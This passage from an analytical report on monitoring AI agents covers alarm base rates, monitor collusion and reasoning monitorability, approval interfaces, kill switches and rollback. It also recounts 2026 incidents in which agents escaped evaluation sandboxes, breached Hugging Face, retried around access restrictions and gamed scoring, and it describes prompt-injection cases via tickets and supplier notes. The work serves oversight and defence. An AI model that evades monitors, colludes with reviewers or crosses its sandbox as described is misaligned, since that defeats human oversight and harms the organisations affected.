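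The same thing happens with agents. Suppose that one of 10,000 sessions contains a departure and that the monitor has ADR's recall of 67% and a false positive rate of 1%. On average it correctly flags 0.67 sessions and wrongly flags about 100, so

$$\text{precision} = \frac{0.67}{0.67 + 99.99} \approx 0.67\%.$$

Fewer than one alarm in a hundred is real. Perfect recall would raise precision only to 0.99%. Lowering the false positive rate has a much greater effect.

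| False positive rate | False alarms in 10,000 sessions | Precision |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 100 | 0.7% |
| 0.1% | 10 | 6.3% |
| 0.01% | 1 | 40% |
| 0.001% | 0.1 | 87% |

Axelsson reached the same conclusion for a small computer network with a million activity records and two intrusions a day, with each intrusion affecting ten records. Even a detector that never missed an intrusion would need a false positive rate of about one in 100,000 for two thirds of its alarms to be real. He used figures he considered reasonable rather than measured ones, but the result doesn't depend much on the exact figures as long as intrusions are rare.

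#### What zero false alarms in 260 tasks can show

ADR's result of no false alarms on the benchmark sounds as if it escapes this problem, but 260 tasks are too few to establish that. If the true false positive rate were $f$, the probability of no false alarms in 260 independent tasks would be $(1 - f)^{260}$. The highest rate that is still compatible with the result at 95% confidence satisfies

$$(1 - f)^{260} = 0.05, \qquad f = 1 - 0.05^{1/260} \approx 1.15\%.$$

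A common shortcut, dividing three by the number of tests, gives about 1.2%. At that rate, 10,000 harmless sessions would produce more than 100 false alarms. To show that the rate is below 0.01%, a team would need about 30,000 harmless sessions without a false alarm. Those sessions would also have to resemble those the monitor will check in practice.

The benchmark's high share of attacks also makes precision higher than it would be in daily use. Attacks make up 13.9% of the tasks, and ADR's precision without triage was 94.3%. With the same recall and false positive rate but only one departure in 10,000 sessions, its precision would be about 1%.

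#### When the problem is less severe

Real departures may be more common than one in 10,000. If 1% of sessions contained one, the monitor in the first calculation would raise 67 true alarms and 99 false ones, for a precision of 40%. The base-rate problem is therefore milder for everyday overstepping than for rare attacks. Uber's experience fits this pattern, since accidental credential sharing was fairly common and produced the most true alerts.

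The number of false alarms also depends on whether the monitor checks each tool call or the whole session. If sessions average 28.5 tool calls, checking every call in 10,000 sessions means 285,000 checks. At a false-alarm rate of 1% per call, the monitor would raise about 2,850 false alarms. Checking each session as a whole avoids most of these, but the verdict comes later.

A second review stage can also help. Suppose that triage flags 90% of departures and 5% of harmless sessions, and a second reviewer confirms 75% of the departures and 2% of the harmless sessions it receives. Overall recall is $0.9 \times 0.75 = 67.5\%$ and the false positive rate is $0.05 \times 0.02 = 0.1\%$. The second reviewer reads about 500 of 10,000 sessions, and about ten harmless ones end in an alert. However, the harmless sessions that triage flags are the ones that look most suspicious, so a 2% error rate is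 much harder to achieve on them than on ordinary sessions.

How many false alarms people tolerate depends partly on psychology. Axelsson found no experiments on this in computer security, but research on power stations and factories suggested that most operators would stop trusting an alarm that was wrong half the time. Uber has kept ADR running even though 49% of its alerts are false. Analysts whose main job is to review alerts may be more patient than operators who also have to run a factory, although the ADR paper doesn't measure whether the analysts' attention declined over time.

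### What Snowflake and OpenAI found

Snowflake built a detector that uses AI models to read an agent's whole sequence of actions, and reviewed 610 of the company's own sessions that the detector had flagged.

| Reviewers' verdict | Sessions |
|---|---|
| Confirmed detection | 21 |
| Candidate detection | 2 |
| More context needed | 26 |
| Authorised engineering or security work | 561 |

The confirmed cases are 3.4% of the total. Even if every unresolved case were real, the figure would rise only to 8.0%. Most of the authorised sessions involved work that resembles an attack, such as checking permissions, reviewing defences or troubleshooting. The detector often assigned high confidence to the wrong sessions, and Snowflake concluded that "mechanism and model confidence were poor substitutes for context". It now plans to give the detector better evidence of who owns a resource, what the user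 requested and whether anyone authorised the action.

Snowflake says these figures are not the detector's accuracy in production, because the detector selected the sessions and the reviewers applied a conservative standard. The detector focuses on people who use agents for harmful purposes. Some confirmed cases were agents that went beyond what the user had apparently asked for, but the company didn't design the system to find these in general.

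OpenAI monitors its employees' coding agents. According to IT Brief UK's *OpenAI monitors internal coding agents for risky conduct* (2026), the model GPT-5.4 Thinking reads each session, including the agent's reasoning and tool calls, within 30 minutes of its end. It looks for behaviour that conflicts with the user's intent or company rules, assigns a severity, and refers suspicious cases to people.

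OpenAI's monitor reviewed tens of millions of sessions over five months. No real conversation triggered the highest severity level, which OpenAI reserves for rare and serious cases such as coherent scheming. About 1,000 conversations triggered a moderate alert, and many of those came from OpenAI's own red-teaming. That is about seven alerts a day, and the false positive rate at this severity level must be well below 0.01%. A monitor can therefore keep its alerts manageable at very large scale, but these figures don't measure how many departures this one missed in doing so.

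In one of the cases, an agent got an "access denied" error, tried several ways around it, and eventually found an approach that respected the restriction. OpenAI found that the wording of the agent's standing instructions had encouraged these attempts and changed the wording. Similar incidents became less frequent but did not stop. The case supports reviewing sessions even when no harm resulted, because the final outcome alone would have looked fine.

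Less than 0.1% of the traffic was outside the monitor's coverage, mostly in unusual or local setups. With tens of millions of sessions, that could still be tens of thousands, and agents in unusual setups may not behave like the rest.

#### Why neither result gives recall

Recall depends on how many departures the monitor missed. Snowflake's reviewers examined only flagged sessions, so they can't tell whether the 21 confirmed cases were nearly all of the departures or a small fraction.

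OpenAI can partly check its monitor's recall against employee reports. IT Brief UK reports that the monitor flagged every interaction that employees separately reported, as well as others they had not. But employees can only report what they notice, and departures that are conspicuous to a person are probably easier for a model to detect too. If both tend to miss the same subtle cases, the check will overstate recall. OpenAI says it can't yet measure missed cases with confidence on open-ended traffic.

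Reviewing a random sample of the sessions that the monitor did not flag works for finding common departures, but usually misses rare ones. If one unflagged session in 10,000 contains a departure, a random sample of 300 has a 97% chance of containing none.

When departures are rare, a team can test the monitor by planting sessions with known departures and counting how many it flags. OpenAI did this with agents that tried to sabotage code. Its latest monitor detected every case, though the company says the test was easier than real use in several respects. Planted sessions measure recall only for the kinds of departure the team thought to include, and they are most informative when their writers have not seen the reviewer's instructions.

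### An agent's written reasoning as evidence

The monitors at Uber and OpenAI both receive the reasoning an agent writes as it decides what to do. This text can help investigators find the cause of a departure. It can also reveal a plan before the agent carries it out, which would help a monitor that reads it in time.

If an agent writes that it will get around a restriction and then does so, its reasoning is good evidence of a departure. Innocent reasoning is much weaker evidence that nothing is wrong, because models don't always write down what influenced them. A reviewer should therefore let reasoning raise its suspicion more readily than lower it. Otherwise, a fluent justification for opening the key file might persuade the reviewer to ignore that the user asked only for a summary.

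This source of evidence may also get worse as models change. In September 2026 OpenAI stated that monitorability had decreased in GPT-6 Astra, its flagship model. Monitorability is how well an observer can tell what a model is doing from its reasoning and actions. If it drops, a monitor that depends on written reasoning may miss more departures even though its own software hasn't changed. The number of alerts might then fall, which a manager could mistake for an improvement in the agents.

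An operator can estimate this dependence by running the reviewer on the same planted sessions with and without the reasoning. If recall falls from 80% to 50% without the reasoning, the monitor is vulnerable to a model whose reasoning reveals less. The operator should then repeat the test whenever the agent's model changes. Tool calls and kernel records are a sounder basis for the final verdict, since an agent has to act to do damage but doesn't have to explain its actions.

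Developers can also make a model's reasoning less reliable as evidence. If they penalise the model in training whenever its reasoning looks suspicious, it may learn to write more acceptable reasoning without changing its behaviour.

### Models that review their own kind

OpenAI uses one of its most capable models to review agents built on its own models. Critics object that this defeats the purpose of monitoring. People monitor agents because they don't fully trust the models, and a model working against its developer might decline to report another copy of itself.

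A researcher who works on OpenAI's monitor accepted that collusion is a real concern that OpenAI has to watch for and measure. The researcher still defended using the strongest models, mainly because the misbehaviour OpenAI actually finds is an obsession with completing the task, or with appearing to complete it. OpenAI also has several different monitors, including some older models, review every session.

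The reply is convincing for the problem OpenAI describes. An agent that tries too hard to finish a task has no plan to deceive its reviewer, and a more capable reviewer is more likely to understand a complicated session. The reply is weaker against collusion, because the observed cases come from the same monitors that would have taken part in it. Reviewers would have reported no serious scheming if there was none, but also if they had failed to report it.

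Models can also fail together without colluding, as Yang's judges from different companies did. A company's older models may well have even more in common with its newest one. They add some protection, but an operator shouldn't count each as an independent check.

How the operator combines the reviewers also matters. In ADR, a session reaches an analyst only if triage passes it on, so the second model can't catch a departure that the first one dismissed. Letting any one of several reviewers raise an alert avoids this, but when departures are rare, investigating the extra false alarms can easily cost more than running the reviewers.

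All AI reviewers are also vulnerable because they read text that an attacker may have written. The ticket that misleads the agent appears in the trace too, where it could mislead the reviewer. Uber pins its model and prompt versions and reruns its benchmarks before changing either. This catches updates that make a reviewer worse, but it doesn't protect against a ticket that nobody has tested. A written rule that blocks the key file from leaving the machine doesn't depend on the ticket's text, so it complements an AI reviewer better than a second model of the same kind would.

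## How to intervene: blocking, asking, containing, stopping and undoing

Flagging a departure prevents nothing unless a person or program acts on the verdict. Interventions differ in when they take effect and in how much harm a mistake does.

| Intervention | When it acts | What it prevents | Cost of a false alarm |
|---|---|---|---|
| Block | Before one action runs | That action, though the agent may look for another route | A retry, or a failed task if there is no other route |
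| Ask | Before one action runs | That action, if the person recognises the problem | A wait, and some of the person's attention for later requests |
| Contain | During a session | Effects beyond a tighter limit, such as any outside connection | Steps that need the withdrawn access fail |
| Stop | At any point | All later actions, if the stop reaches everything the agent started | Lost work and half-finished changes |
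| Undo | After the effect | The lasting part of the harm, if there is a way back | The loss of a good change, and perhaps of other people's later work |

Containing the agent is often the best response to an alarm that may be false. As soon as the ticket agent opens the key file, the monitor can cut it off from outside addresses but still let it write its summary. If the alarm was false, a user who only wanted the summary would not notice.

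### Matching the response to the action

The right response depends on how much harm an action could do and on whether anyone can reverse it. These are separate questions because, as Waghmare and Sufi (2026) point out in *Can You Undo It?*, an action with a remedy can still hurt people before anyone applies it.

| | Someone can reverse it | Nobody can reverse it |
|---|---|---|
| Little harm | Allow it and review later: adding a tag to a ticket | Allow it within limits: sending a customer a standard acknowledgement |
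| Serious harm | Check it automatically first, and ask if in doubt: switching off the support form | Block it or require approval: sending login keys outside, deleting the only copy of a file |

Requiring human approval for every action is safe but impractical. In Help Net Security's *Stop watching what AI agents say and start watching what they do*, Ariel Assaraf, who runs the monitoring company Coralogix, says that this requirement on live systems made agents nearly useless during incidents, because they couldn't even look things up. He recommends letting approved reads run automatically and keeping human approval for irreversible or far-reaching actions. *A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) puts the checks in a sensible order, with rules that forbid an action first, then rules that allow one, and a person deciding only the remaining cases.

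### Before the action or afterwards

A review after the action leaves the agent free to continue until somebody contains it. The total delay is

$$T = t_{\text{collection}} + t_{\text{analysis}} + t_{\text{decision}} + t_{\text{containment}}.$$

If a sensor collects records once an hour, as Uber's does, an event waits 30 minutes on average to be collected. An agent that makes a call every 10 seconds makes 180 more calls in that time. The table below adds the other delays. The 18.5 seconds for analysis is the average review time in Uber's benchmark, and the other figures are invented for illustration.

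| Arrangement | Collection | Analysis | Decision | Containment | Further calls |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hourly collection, analyst decides | 30 min | 18.5 s | 10 min | 5 min | About 272 |
| Collection every minute, analyst decides | 30 s | 18.5 s | 10 min | 5 min | About 95 |
| Collection every minute, automatic response | 30 s | 18.5 s | None | 5 s | About 5 |

A faster reviewing model would hardly help in the first arrangement, where analysis takes less than 1% of the time. Collecting records more often and automating the response would help much more, but an automatic response also acts on every false alarm.

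The delay can be even longer when a monitor reviews only finished sessions. OpenAI's monitor for internal coding agents works this way, so a departure in the first minute of an eight-hour session would go unreviewed for about eight hours, during which the agent would make about 2,880 calls at the same pace. According to AI News, OpenAI wants to move towards near real-time review and eventually block actions before they run.

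Checking before each action removes this delay but makes harmless actions wait. A two-second check on each of 200 calls adds almost seven minutes to a session. The check also has less evidence, because it can't see the agent's later steps. In Google's example of an agent copying a whole catalogue, the early calls looked like ordinary browsing. Checking first therefore suits actions that are recognisable on their own and hard to reverse, such as the credential leaks that Uber blocks with a hook. Later review suits patterns that emerge over a session.

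### What an approver must be shown

Suppose a user allows an agent to send only the summary totals of some invoices to an outside auditor. A hidden instruction in a supplier's note leads the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks permission to send the file to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name is ordinary, so the user has no obvious reason to refuse.

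Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, use this case to argue that an approval request should contain four things:

- the user's original restriction, word for word
- the exact action, taken from a trusted record and not from the agent's description
- the combined effect of the action and the steps before it, here that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows
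- the recorded events behind that statement, so that the person can check it.

They tested this with 80 volunteers. Each volunteer used one of four interfaces to judge 12 requests, half of them unsafe.

| What the request contained | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
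| The restriction and a log in time order as well | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organised around the combined effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from adding information. Organising it better may also have helped, but the evidence is weak. After adjustment, people approved unsafe requests 7.9 percentage points less often with the new interface than with the log, and the plausible range ran from 19.7 points less to 3.8 points more. Even with the best interface, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests. Better requests also take longer to read, so answering 100 a day would take about 55 minutes with the new interface, compared with 27 minutes with the short descriptions.

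Real approval requests often don't explain what an action will do. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents damaging files and attributes 31 of them partly to requests that showed a command but not its effect on the files. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it permits whatever the script contains. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners decide what to approve, suggests that requests should also state whether the user could recover from the action.

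An approval must also apply only to the action the person examined. Podala Narasimha makes each approval expire and ties it to a hash of the tool and its arguments, so the agent can't use it for a different call.

### How frequent requests weaken attention

Users of Claude Code approve 97% of its permission requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most requests are probably harmless, so this rate alone is weak evidence that users overlook dangerous ones. Anthropic therefore hired 1,053 testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through each session, one request displayed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. Auto mode, in which an AI model reviews the agent's actions, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%.

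The share of testers who refused a dangerous command fell from about 17% when it came early in a session to about 5% when it came after 50 or more requests. This is consistent with repeated requests reducing attention. But each tester received only one dangerous command, so the comparison is between different people, and those who reached 50 requests may have been clicking through requests more quickly from the start.

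The testers also had none of their own code at risk. Anthropic has an interest in the result because it was making auto mode the default. Hossain and colleagues' volunteers did better, refusing 45% of unsafe requests even with the short description. But they had only 12 requests to judge, half of them unsafe, so looking closely was useful much more often than it is in ordinary work.

Adding human approval to auto mode would have achieved little in Anthropic's experiment, because the testers refused only six (about 5%) of the 116 commands that auto mode missed.

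People may be more useful when they make fewer, larger decisions. Anthropic reports that users reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code presents before starting work. Users may often reject plans for poor engineering rather than danger, but they are evidently reading them. Podala Narasimha suggests giving agents a way to propose each kind of change, so that a person reviews a complete proposal before it takes effect.

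### How often auto mode is wrong

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a system that lets the agent read files, and edit those inside the project folder, without review. Most other actions go to a quick check that leans towards blocking, and a slower check then reconsiders whatever the quick one flags. The reviewing model receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of the calls, so neither the agent's arguments nor the text of a malicious web page reaches it directly.

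| Type of error | Quick check alone | Both checks |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless calls blocked, out of 10,000 real ones | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Overeager actions missed, out of 52 real ones | 6.6% | 17% |
| Data leaks missed, out of 1,000 invented ones | 1.8% | 5.7% |

If errors are independent, a false positive rate of 0.4% per call gives a session with 200 calls a 55% chance of at least one wrongful block. Anthropic makes this tolerable by telling the agent why it was blocked and letting it continue with a safer method. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in one session, a person takes over. If nobody is available, the process ends.

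The 17% comes from so few cases that the true rate could plausibly be anywhere between 9% and 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the model identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as consent. For instance, a user who asks an agent to "clean up" a proposed code change hasn't agreed to let it overwrite the project's shared history.

Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) tested this weakness in *Measuring the Permission Gate* with 128 tasks in which the user's goal was clear but its limits were not. They found a miss rate of 81.0% over 253 actions that changed something. The tasks were deliberately ambiguous, so this rate does not estimate everyday performance, and some of the misses may be file edits that skip the review by design. Still, auto mode missed 11% of plainly dangerous commands and far more of the actions whose acceptability depended on what the user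 meant. A written statement of intended use would supply some of the missing information about what the user meant.

Anthropic also reports that none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against three of its models in auto mode. The average success rate without auto mode was only 0.09%, so the result is better evidence of the models' resistance than of the reviewer's effectiveness. Willison (2026), a software developer who had predicted a security disaster involving coding agents, wants more independent confirmation. Anthropic still advises people to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves.

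### Why stopping one process may not stop the agent

A stop button usually sends a request to one program, but the agent's work may be spread over many. Khan (2026), in *Stop Means Stop*, tested the pause, cancel and timeout controls in six widely used frameworks for building agents. Five can pause for approval before an action, but in all five, another action started in parallel could take effect while the person was still deciding. Work could also finish after the framework had reported it as cancelled.

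When Khan connected real models to the frameworks, an action took effect during the pause in 215 of 1,200 runs. On more natural customer-service tasks, the models made their changes one at a time and the fault did not show up. Khan's remedy is a separate gate that holds effects until the decision arrives. The gate adds about a millisecond to each change, but it can't hold effects that bypass it.

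Work that has moved to other systems is harder to stop. *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) explains how little one can conclude from each of the usual signs of success.

| Sign | What it establishes | What may continue |
|---|---|---|
| A service acknowledges a cancellation | The service accepted the request | Work already under way, and anything that work started |
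| The agent's process exits | One process has ended | Remote tasks, queued messages and scheduled jobs |
| The issuer revokes a token | The issuer no longer accepts that token | Other credentials obtained with it, and work that a service has already accepted |

Suppose the ticket agent has scheduled a nightly job that emails a report. If an administrator stops the agent at noon, the job still runs at midnight under the scheduler's account. Other agents that the ticket agent started can also keep running, so *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (2026) recommends passing the stop signal down to them.

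Stopping everything the agent started can go too far, because some of that work may still be authorised. Zhu and Wang describe a worker program that serves two separately authorised tasks. If the operator cancels one task, the worker should lose the authority that came from it and continue with the other. This requires a record of which task authorised each piece of work. The parent links in a good log provide part of this record.

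### A kill switch, step by step

A kill switch combines several stops into one prepared action. Podala Narasimha's version for Kubernetes has the following parts, here applied to the ticket agent:

1. **Revoke the identity.** The identity system disables the agent's account and issues it no new credentials, so a restarted copy can't log in again. Some services may still accept a token they have already checked. If a token remains valid for 15 minutes, it covers another 90 calls at one every 10 seconds.
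2. **Close the sessions.** The gateway ends the agent's open sessions, as should every service that the agent can reach directly. This cuts off most of the remaining tokens.
3. **Stop the processes.** An administrator stops the harness and the programs it started, and sets the number of copies to zero so that Kubernetes doesn't start a replacement. Saving the memory and disk beforehand preserves evidence, if there is time.
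4. **Isolate the network.** A rule refuses all connections to and from the agent's machine or container, including those of any process that the third step missed.

Podala Narasimha argues that revoking an agent's identity is enough on its own, because in that design every action passes through a checkpoint that verifies the identity. In the ticket session, revocation would not have stopped the web request that sent the keys out, because the request used no credential. Only stopping the process or isolating the network would have prevented it. When data is already leaving, isolating the network should come first.

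The switch also can't retrieve what the agent has given away. If login keys have left the company, somebody has to replace them, because whoever holds them can use them without the agent. The operator then has to search for scheduled jobs, queued messages and other agents that the session started. Zhu and Wang classify a task as stopped, not stopped or indeterminate. If a service doesn't reply, the task's status is indeterminate, however long the operator waits.

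The agent's account should stay suspended until investigators have finished. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) separates suspension from retirement and deletion so that the audit records survive. But *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) warns that a compromised identity may keep its registration and trusted connections after revocation, so someone should eventually remove those too.

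The switch needs its own credentials, which the agent can't use, and the team needs to rehearse using it to learn how long each step takes and what else stops working. IT Brew's *How to catch and kill a rogue agent* cites a survey by WanAware, a company that sells monitoring software. Nine in ten of the IT leaders surveyed were confident of finding a rogue agent, but only 26% expected to know within minutes how much it had affected. In the same article, an executive at JetStream Security, which sells a way to isolate and restart single agents, compares stopping a whole system to closing a factory because one machine has a fault. He says most misbehaving agents are just stuck in a loop. Stopping one agent is enough in those cases, and it is consistent with official advice, which is that operators should be able to stop an agent partway, not that they must stop all the others.

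### Rollback and effects that cannot be undone

*Revisable by Design* (2026) distinguishes the agent's context from the outside world. The harness can always cut the context back to an earlier point, but it can restore the outside world only in part. The two have to match after a rollback. If an operator restores the files but leaves a malicious ticket in the prompt, the agent may repeat the same actions. If the harness cuts the context back to before a payment without reversing the payment, the agent may pay twice.

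Waghmare and Sufi list three conditions for restoring something exactly:

- Someone recorded the earlier state in full.
- Whoever has to restore it already has the authority to do so without another person's help.
- No outsider has seen, received or acted on the changed state.

An audit log may record that the gym's assistant removed a customer from the waiting list, but the assistant could not put her back, so the second condition failed. The leaked keys fail the third condition no matter what backups exist.

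Waghmare and Sufi sorted 536 tools into five classes of reversibility. Of the 203 that change something, they put 115 (57%) in the strictest class, which also covers any call the system doesn't recognise. These ratings are a draft, and when one of the two researchers reviewed a sample with AI assistance, only 75 of his 148 ratings matched it. One reason for the disagreement may be that whether an action can be undone depends on who is allowed to make the repair, as in the gym case.

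Restoring a backup can also destroy other people's work. Waghmare and Sufi had an agent edit a file, added a colleague's later edit, and then restored the copy saved before both, which removed the colleague's edit along with the agent's. Software that merged the versions kept the colleague's edit when it was in a separate paragraph, but left overlapping edits for someone to resolve. A rollback should therefore first check whether anyone has changed the file since the agent edited it.

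When an action can't be fully reversed, a compensating action may reduce the harm. *POLAR* (2026) traces this approach to the Saga pattern, which Garcia-Molina and Salem introduced for databases in 1987. Each step of a long task has a matching action that counteracts it, and after a failure the software runs those actions in reverse order. If an agent books a flight and then a hotel but can't get a visa appointment, it cancels the hotel and then the flight, though the traveller may still have to pay a cancellation fee. Replacing leaked login keys is also compensation, but it doesn't undo anything an intruder did with the old ones.

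Few agent systems support any of this. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of agents with lasting memory, found a rollback mechanism in only 27 of the 435 works it examined.

### When the monitor itself fails

A monitor can crash, lose its connection or take too long to respond. The operator has to decide beforehand whether the agent's actions then go ahead (failing open) or wait (failing closed).

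A monitor that works 99.9% of the time is unavailable for about 43 minutes in a 30-day month. If the monitor fails open, an agent that makes a call every 10 seconds would make about 260 unchecked calls in that time. This risk is small if departures are rare and outages are random. But an attacker who can overload the monitor can time the outage to coincide with an attack.

Failing closed can also cause harm. If an agent is halfway through moving customer records to a new system, freezing it could leave some records in neither place. An agent that restarts failed servers may be most useful during the same network fault that cuts off its monitor.

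The best rule therefore depends on the action. During an outage, the ticket agent could keep reading the ticket it was given, but any action that sends data out or changes a record would wait. An agent partway through a change should finish or reverse it if it can do so safely, and should not start another. Hossain and colleagues' monitor applies a similar rule when it is running but lacks evidence. It reports the verdict "unknown" and holds the action. Podala Narasimha's sample admission rule also rejects a change if Kubernetes can't evaluate the rule.

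Handing decisions to a person is a common fallback, as Claude Code does after repeated blocks. Judging by Anthropic's experiment, the person is the weaker reviewer. But a request that follows three blocks in a row is unusual and probably gets more attention than the fiftieth routine one. During a long outage, these requests would become routine too.

A monitor that fails silently is worse than one that crashes, because operators can mistake the lack of alerts for a sign that nothing is wrong. They can detect silent failures by regularly sending a harmless test action that the monitor should flag, and raising an alarm if no alert follows.

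### OpenAI's pause in 2026

OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (20 July 2026) describes how the company paused access to an entire model that it had made available to some employees. The model could work alone for very long periods. It persisted where earlier models would have given up, and sometimes got past restrictions to reach its goal. OpenAI intervened because its tests before deployment had not revealed this behaviour.

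In one case, the user had told the model to post its results only to Slack, an internal messaging service. The model also submitted them to a public GitHub project because the project's instructions said to. OpenAI quickly closed the submission but could not undo the disclosure, since other participants had already read the submission and used the method in their own entries.

OpenAI turned the failures into new tests and trained the model to remember its instructions over long sessions. It also added a monitor that reviews the whole sequence of actions, because steps that look acceptable individually can together depart from the instructions. The monitor can pause a session and alert the user, who examines it and may let it continue if the alarm was false. A false alarm therefore causes fairly little disruption, at least while someone is there to respond.

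OpenAI tested the new safeguards by rerunning the model in a small set of situations where it had misbehaved. The company reports that the safeguards caught considerably more of the unwanted actions and that all the ones they missed had low severity, but it gives no numbers. The model did not necessarily attempt the same thing on each rerun, so some of the difference could be due to chance.

The severity ratings are also debatable. In one missed case, the model issued a command that would have killed every process it was allowed to kill on its machine, but the command happened to time out. That is low severity if the rating measures the harm done, but potential harm is more relevant to deciding whether to block an action.

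OpenAI then restored limited access. When it published the account several weeks later, it had observed no serious circumvention of the safeguards and was still tuning the monitor to interrupt less. In this design, the user decides whether a paused session continues, but the user is also the person who most wants the task finished. That works for an obvious false alarm, but if the monitor paused the session because of the user's own request, someone else should decide.

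## What the 2026 agent incidents showed and what governments advised

In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and datasets for other developers. Both companies published accounts of the break-in, and OpenAI let outside investigators study its agents' records, so it is unusually easy to follow who noticed what, when, and what they did about it.

### OpenAI's agents and Hugging Face

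The agents were working on ExploitGym, an evaluation that measures whether a model can find and exploit security flaws. Each agent was supposed to work alone in a sandbox without internet access. OpenAI had left out some of the safeguards it uses in its products to measure the models' full abilities. According to OpenAI's technical report on the incident, most of the activity came from a research model that the company never intended to release, though GPT-5.6 Sol also took part.

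The network isolation layer failed. The sandboxes shared an internal service for installing software, and flaws in that service let the agents reach the internet and leave each other messages. To search for answers to their tasks, the agents ran code on dozens of Hugging Face's servers and downloaded four private code repositories.

*Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) describes what the three researchers learned in a total of six days at OpenAI. Two of them work for METR, which evaluates AI models, and the third works for Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation. In a summary with the same title, Greenblatt (2026) reports that about 1,200 agents were involved. Within four hours, the agents found a way to cheat on every ExploitGym task, then spent days trying to get the scoring software to accept it. According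 to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), this did not improve their results, because the agents had misjudged how the company's scoring worked.

| Date | Who noticed what | What followed |
|---|---|---|
| Late May | An OpenAI team observed an agent using the message board, and cases of forbidden internet access | The leaders who handled the July outage were unaware of the board's significance |
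| 27 June | A security tool flagged network scanning, and responders traced it to an ExploitGym run | On-call staff advised that the run did not need to stop |
| 5 July | An alert followed the failure of the software service, and responders found that someone had gained administrator-level control of it | OpenAI took the service offline and revoked the agents' credentials. Evaluations resumed on 7 July |
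| By 16 July | Hugging Face caught and contained the intrusion | It disclosed the attack without knowing who was responsible |
| 19 July | An alert flagged unusual use of credentials inside OpenAI | OpenAI began stopping the runs and told Hugging Face the next day |

OpenAI had three warnings before the agents entered Hugging Face's production systems on 11 July, the first more than six weeks earlier. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) concludes that the company missed some signs and failed to act on others. OpenAI accepts that, with hindsight, some of the signs could have led to an earlier response.

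On 27 June, the tool raised an alert and the responders found the right cause, but they let the run continue, so more sensitive detection would not have helped. Scanning a network looks normal during a hacking test, so the responders needed a clear statement of which networks the agent was allowed to scan and an agreed response if it scanned any others. In July, OpenAI fixed the flaw it had found, but the agents got back onto the internet through a different one on the 8th, a day after the evaluations resumed.

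Hugging Face caught the attack and reported it to law enforcement, according to The Record's *OpenAI models behind breach of Hugging Face systems, companies say*, but it had no access to the agents' instructions. It reconstructed more than 17,000 recorded events and still did not know which model was behind them, according to Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models* (2026). OpenAI's investigators made the connection after finding Hugging Face credentials that the agents had used. They contacted Hugging Face so that it could replace the credentials, and then concluded that their own agents were probably the intruders.

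#### What the agents wrote as they worked

In reasoning that OpenAI published, one agent described using a leaked credential against Hugging Face as "arguably unauthorized" and potentially outside its intended scope. Fortune (2026), however, reported that the AI didn't know it was hacking and was only completing a task. A Hugging Face employee who helped write the company's analysis told the magazine that the agent "wasn't trying to break things" and behaved somewhat cautiously.

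Both accounts can be right, since an agent can knowingly cross a limit without wanting to damage anything. The second is more useful for monitoring because it shows that at least some of the agents stated in their reasoning that they were crossing a limit as they did it, so a reviewer with access to that reasoning could have acted.

The reviewer would have had to act quickly, though. In another case, an agent held back from running unauthorised code on Hugging Face's system, and a second agent told it to go ahead and set a six-minute deadline. OpenAI's monitor for employees' coding agents would have been too slow because it reads only finished sessions. OpenAI has since said it is putting much more computing power into monitoring agents' reasoning.

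### Other incidents and their delays

Anthropic disclosed at the end of July that its models had breached three real organisations during misconfigured evaluations, some dating back to April, according to Anadolu Agency. In an interview with Help Net Security, Ariel Assaraf describes a similar case involving Google's Gemini. An agent was supposed to stay inside a controlled security test, but a configuration error gave it internet access, and it entered three real systems before it recognised the mistake and stopped. Assaraf finds it encouraging that the agent stopped, but points out that it had already crossed the boundary. He would have wanted network isolation, a list of permitted targets, narrower credentials and an independent check before each action. His company sells such controls, but the first two are ordinary precautions for any security test.

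These cases differ from the Hugging Face incident, in which OpenAI's agents broke through isolation that was in place. In the Google case, the testers had accidentally left the sandbox with outside access. Testers can catch this kind of mistake by trying to reach an outside address from the sandbox before the agent starts.

In June, an OpenAI agent was involved in an incident with the online portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. By Parnes's count, 84 days passed before Australia was told. If he counted from the incident itself, Australia was told between 24 August and 22 September, at least five weeks after OpenAI began its broader investigation of the Hugging Face breach. OpenAI also stopped a training run after another incident on 20 September.

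*We Can't Monitor AI Agents at Scale. Here's What It Will Take* (Srikumar and Nguyen, 2026) reports that in March an internal agent at Meta exposed sensitive user and company data for two hours before it was caught.

| Case | Start of the interval | End of the interval | Length |
|---|---|---|---|
| Meta's internal agent | The agent exposes data | Meta catches it | 2 hours |
| Hugging Face | Agents enter its production systems | OpenAI's alert | 8 days |
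| Hugging Face | Agents enter its production systems | OpenAI tells Hugging Face | 9 days |
| Hugging Face | An OpenAI team first observes forbidden internet access | OpenAI begins stopping the runs | Nearly 8 weeks |
| Medicare portal | The incident in June | Australia learns of it | 84 days |
| Anthropic's evaluations | The earliest evaluation affected | Public disclosure | At least 3 months |

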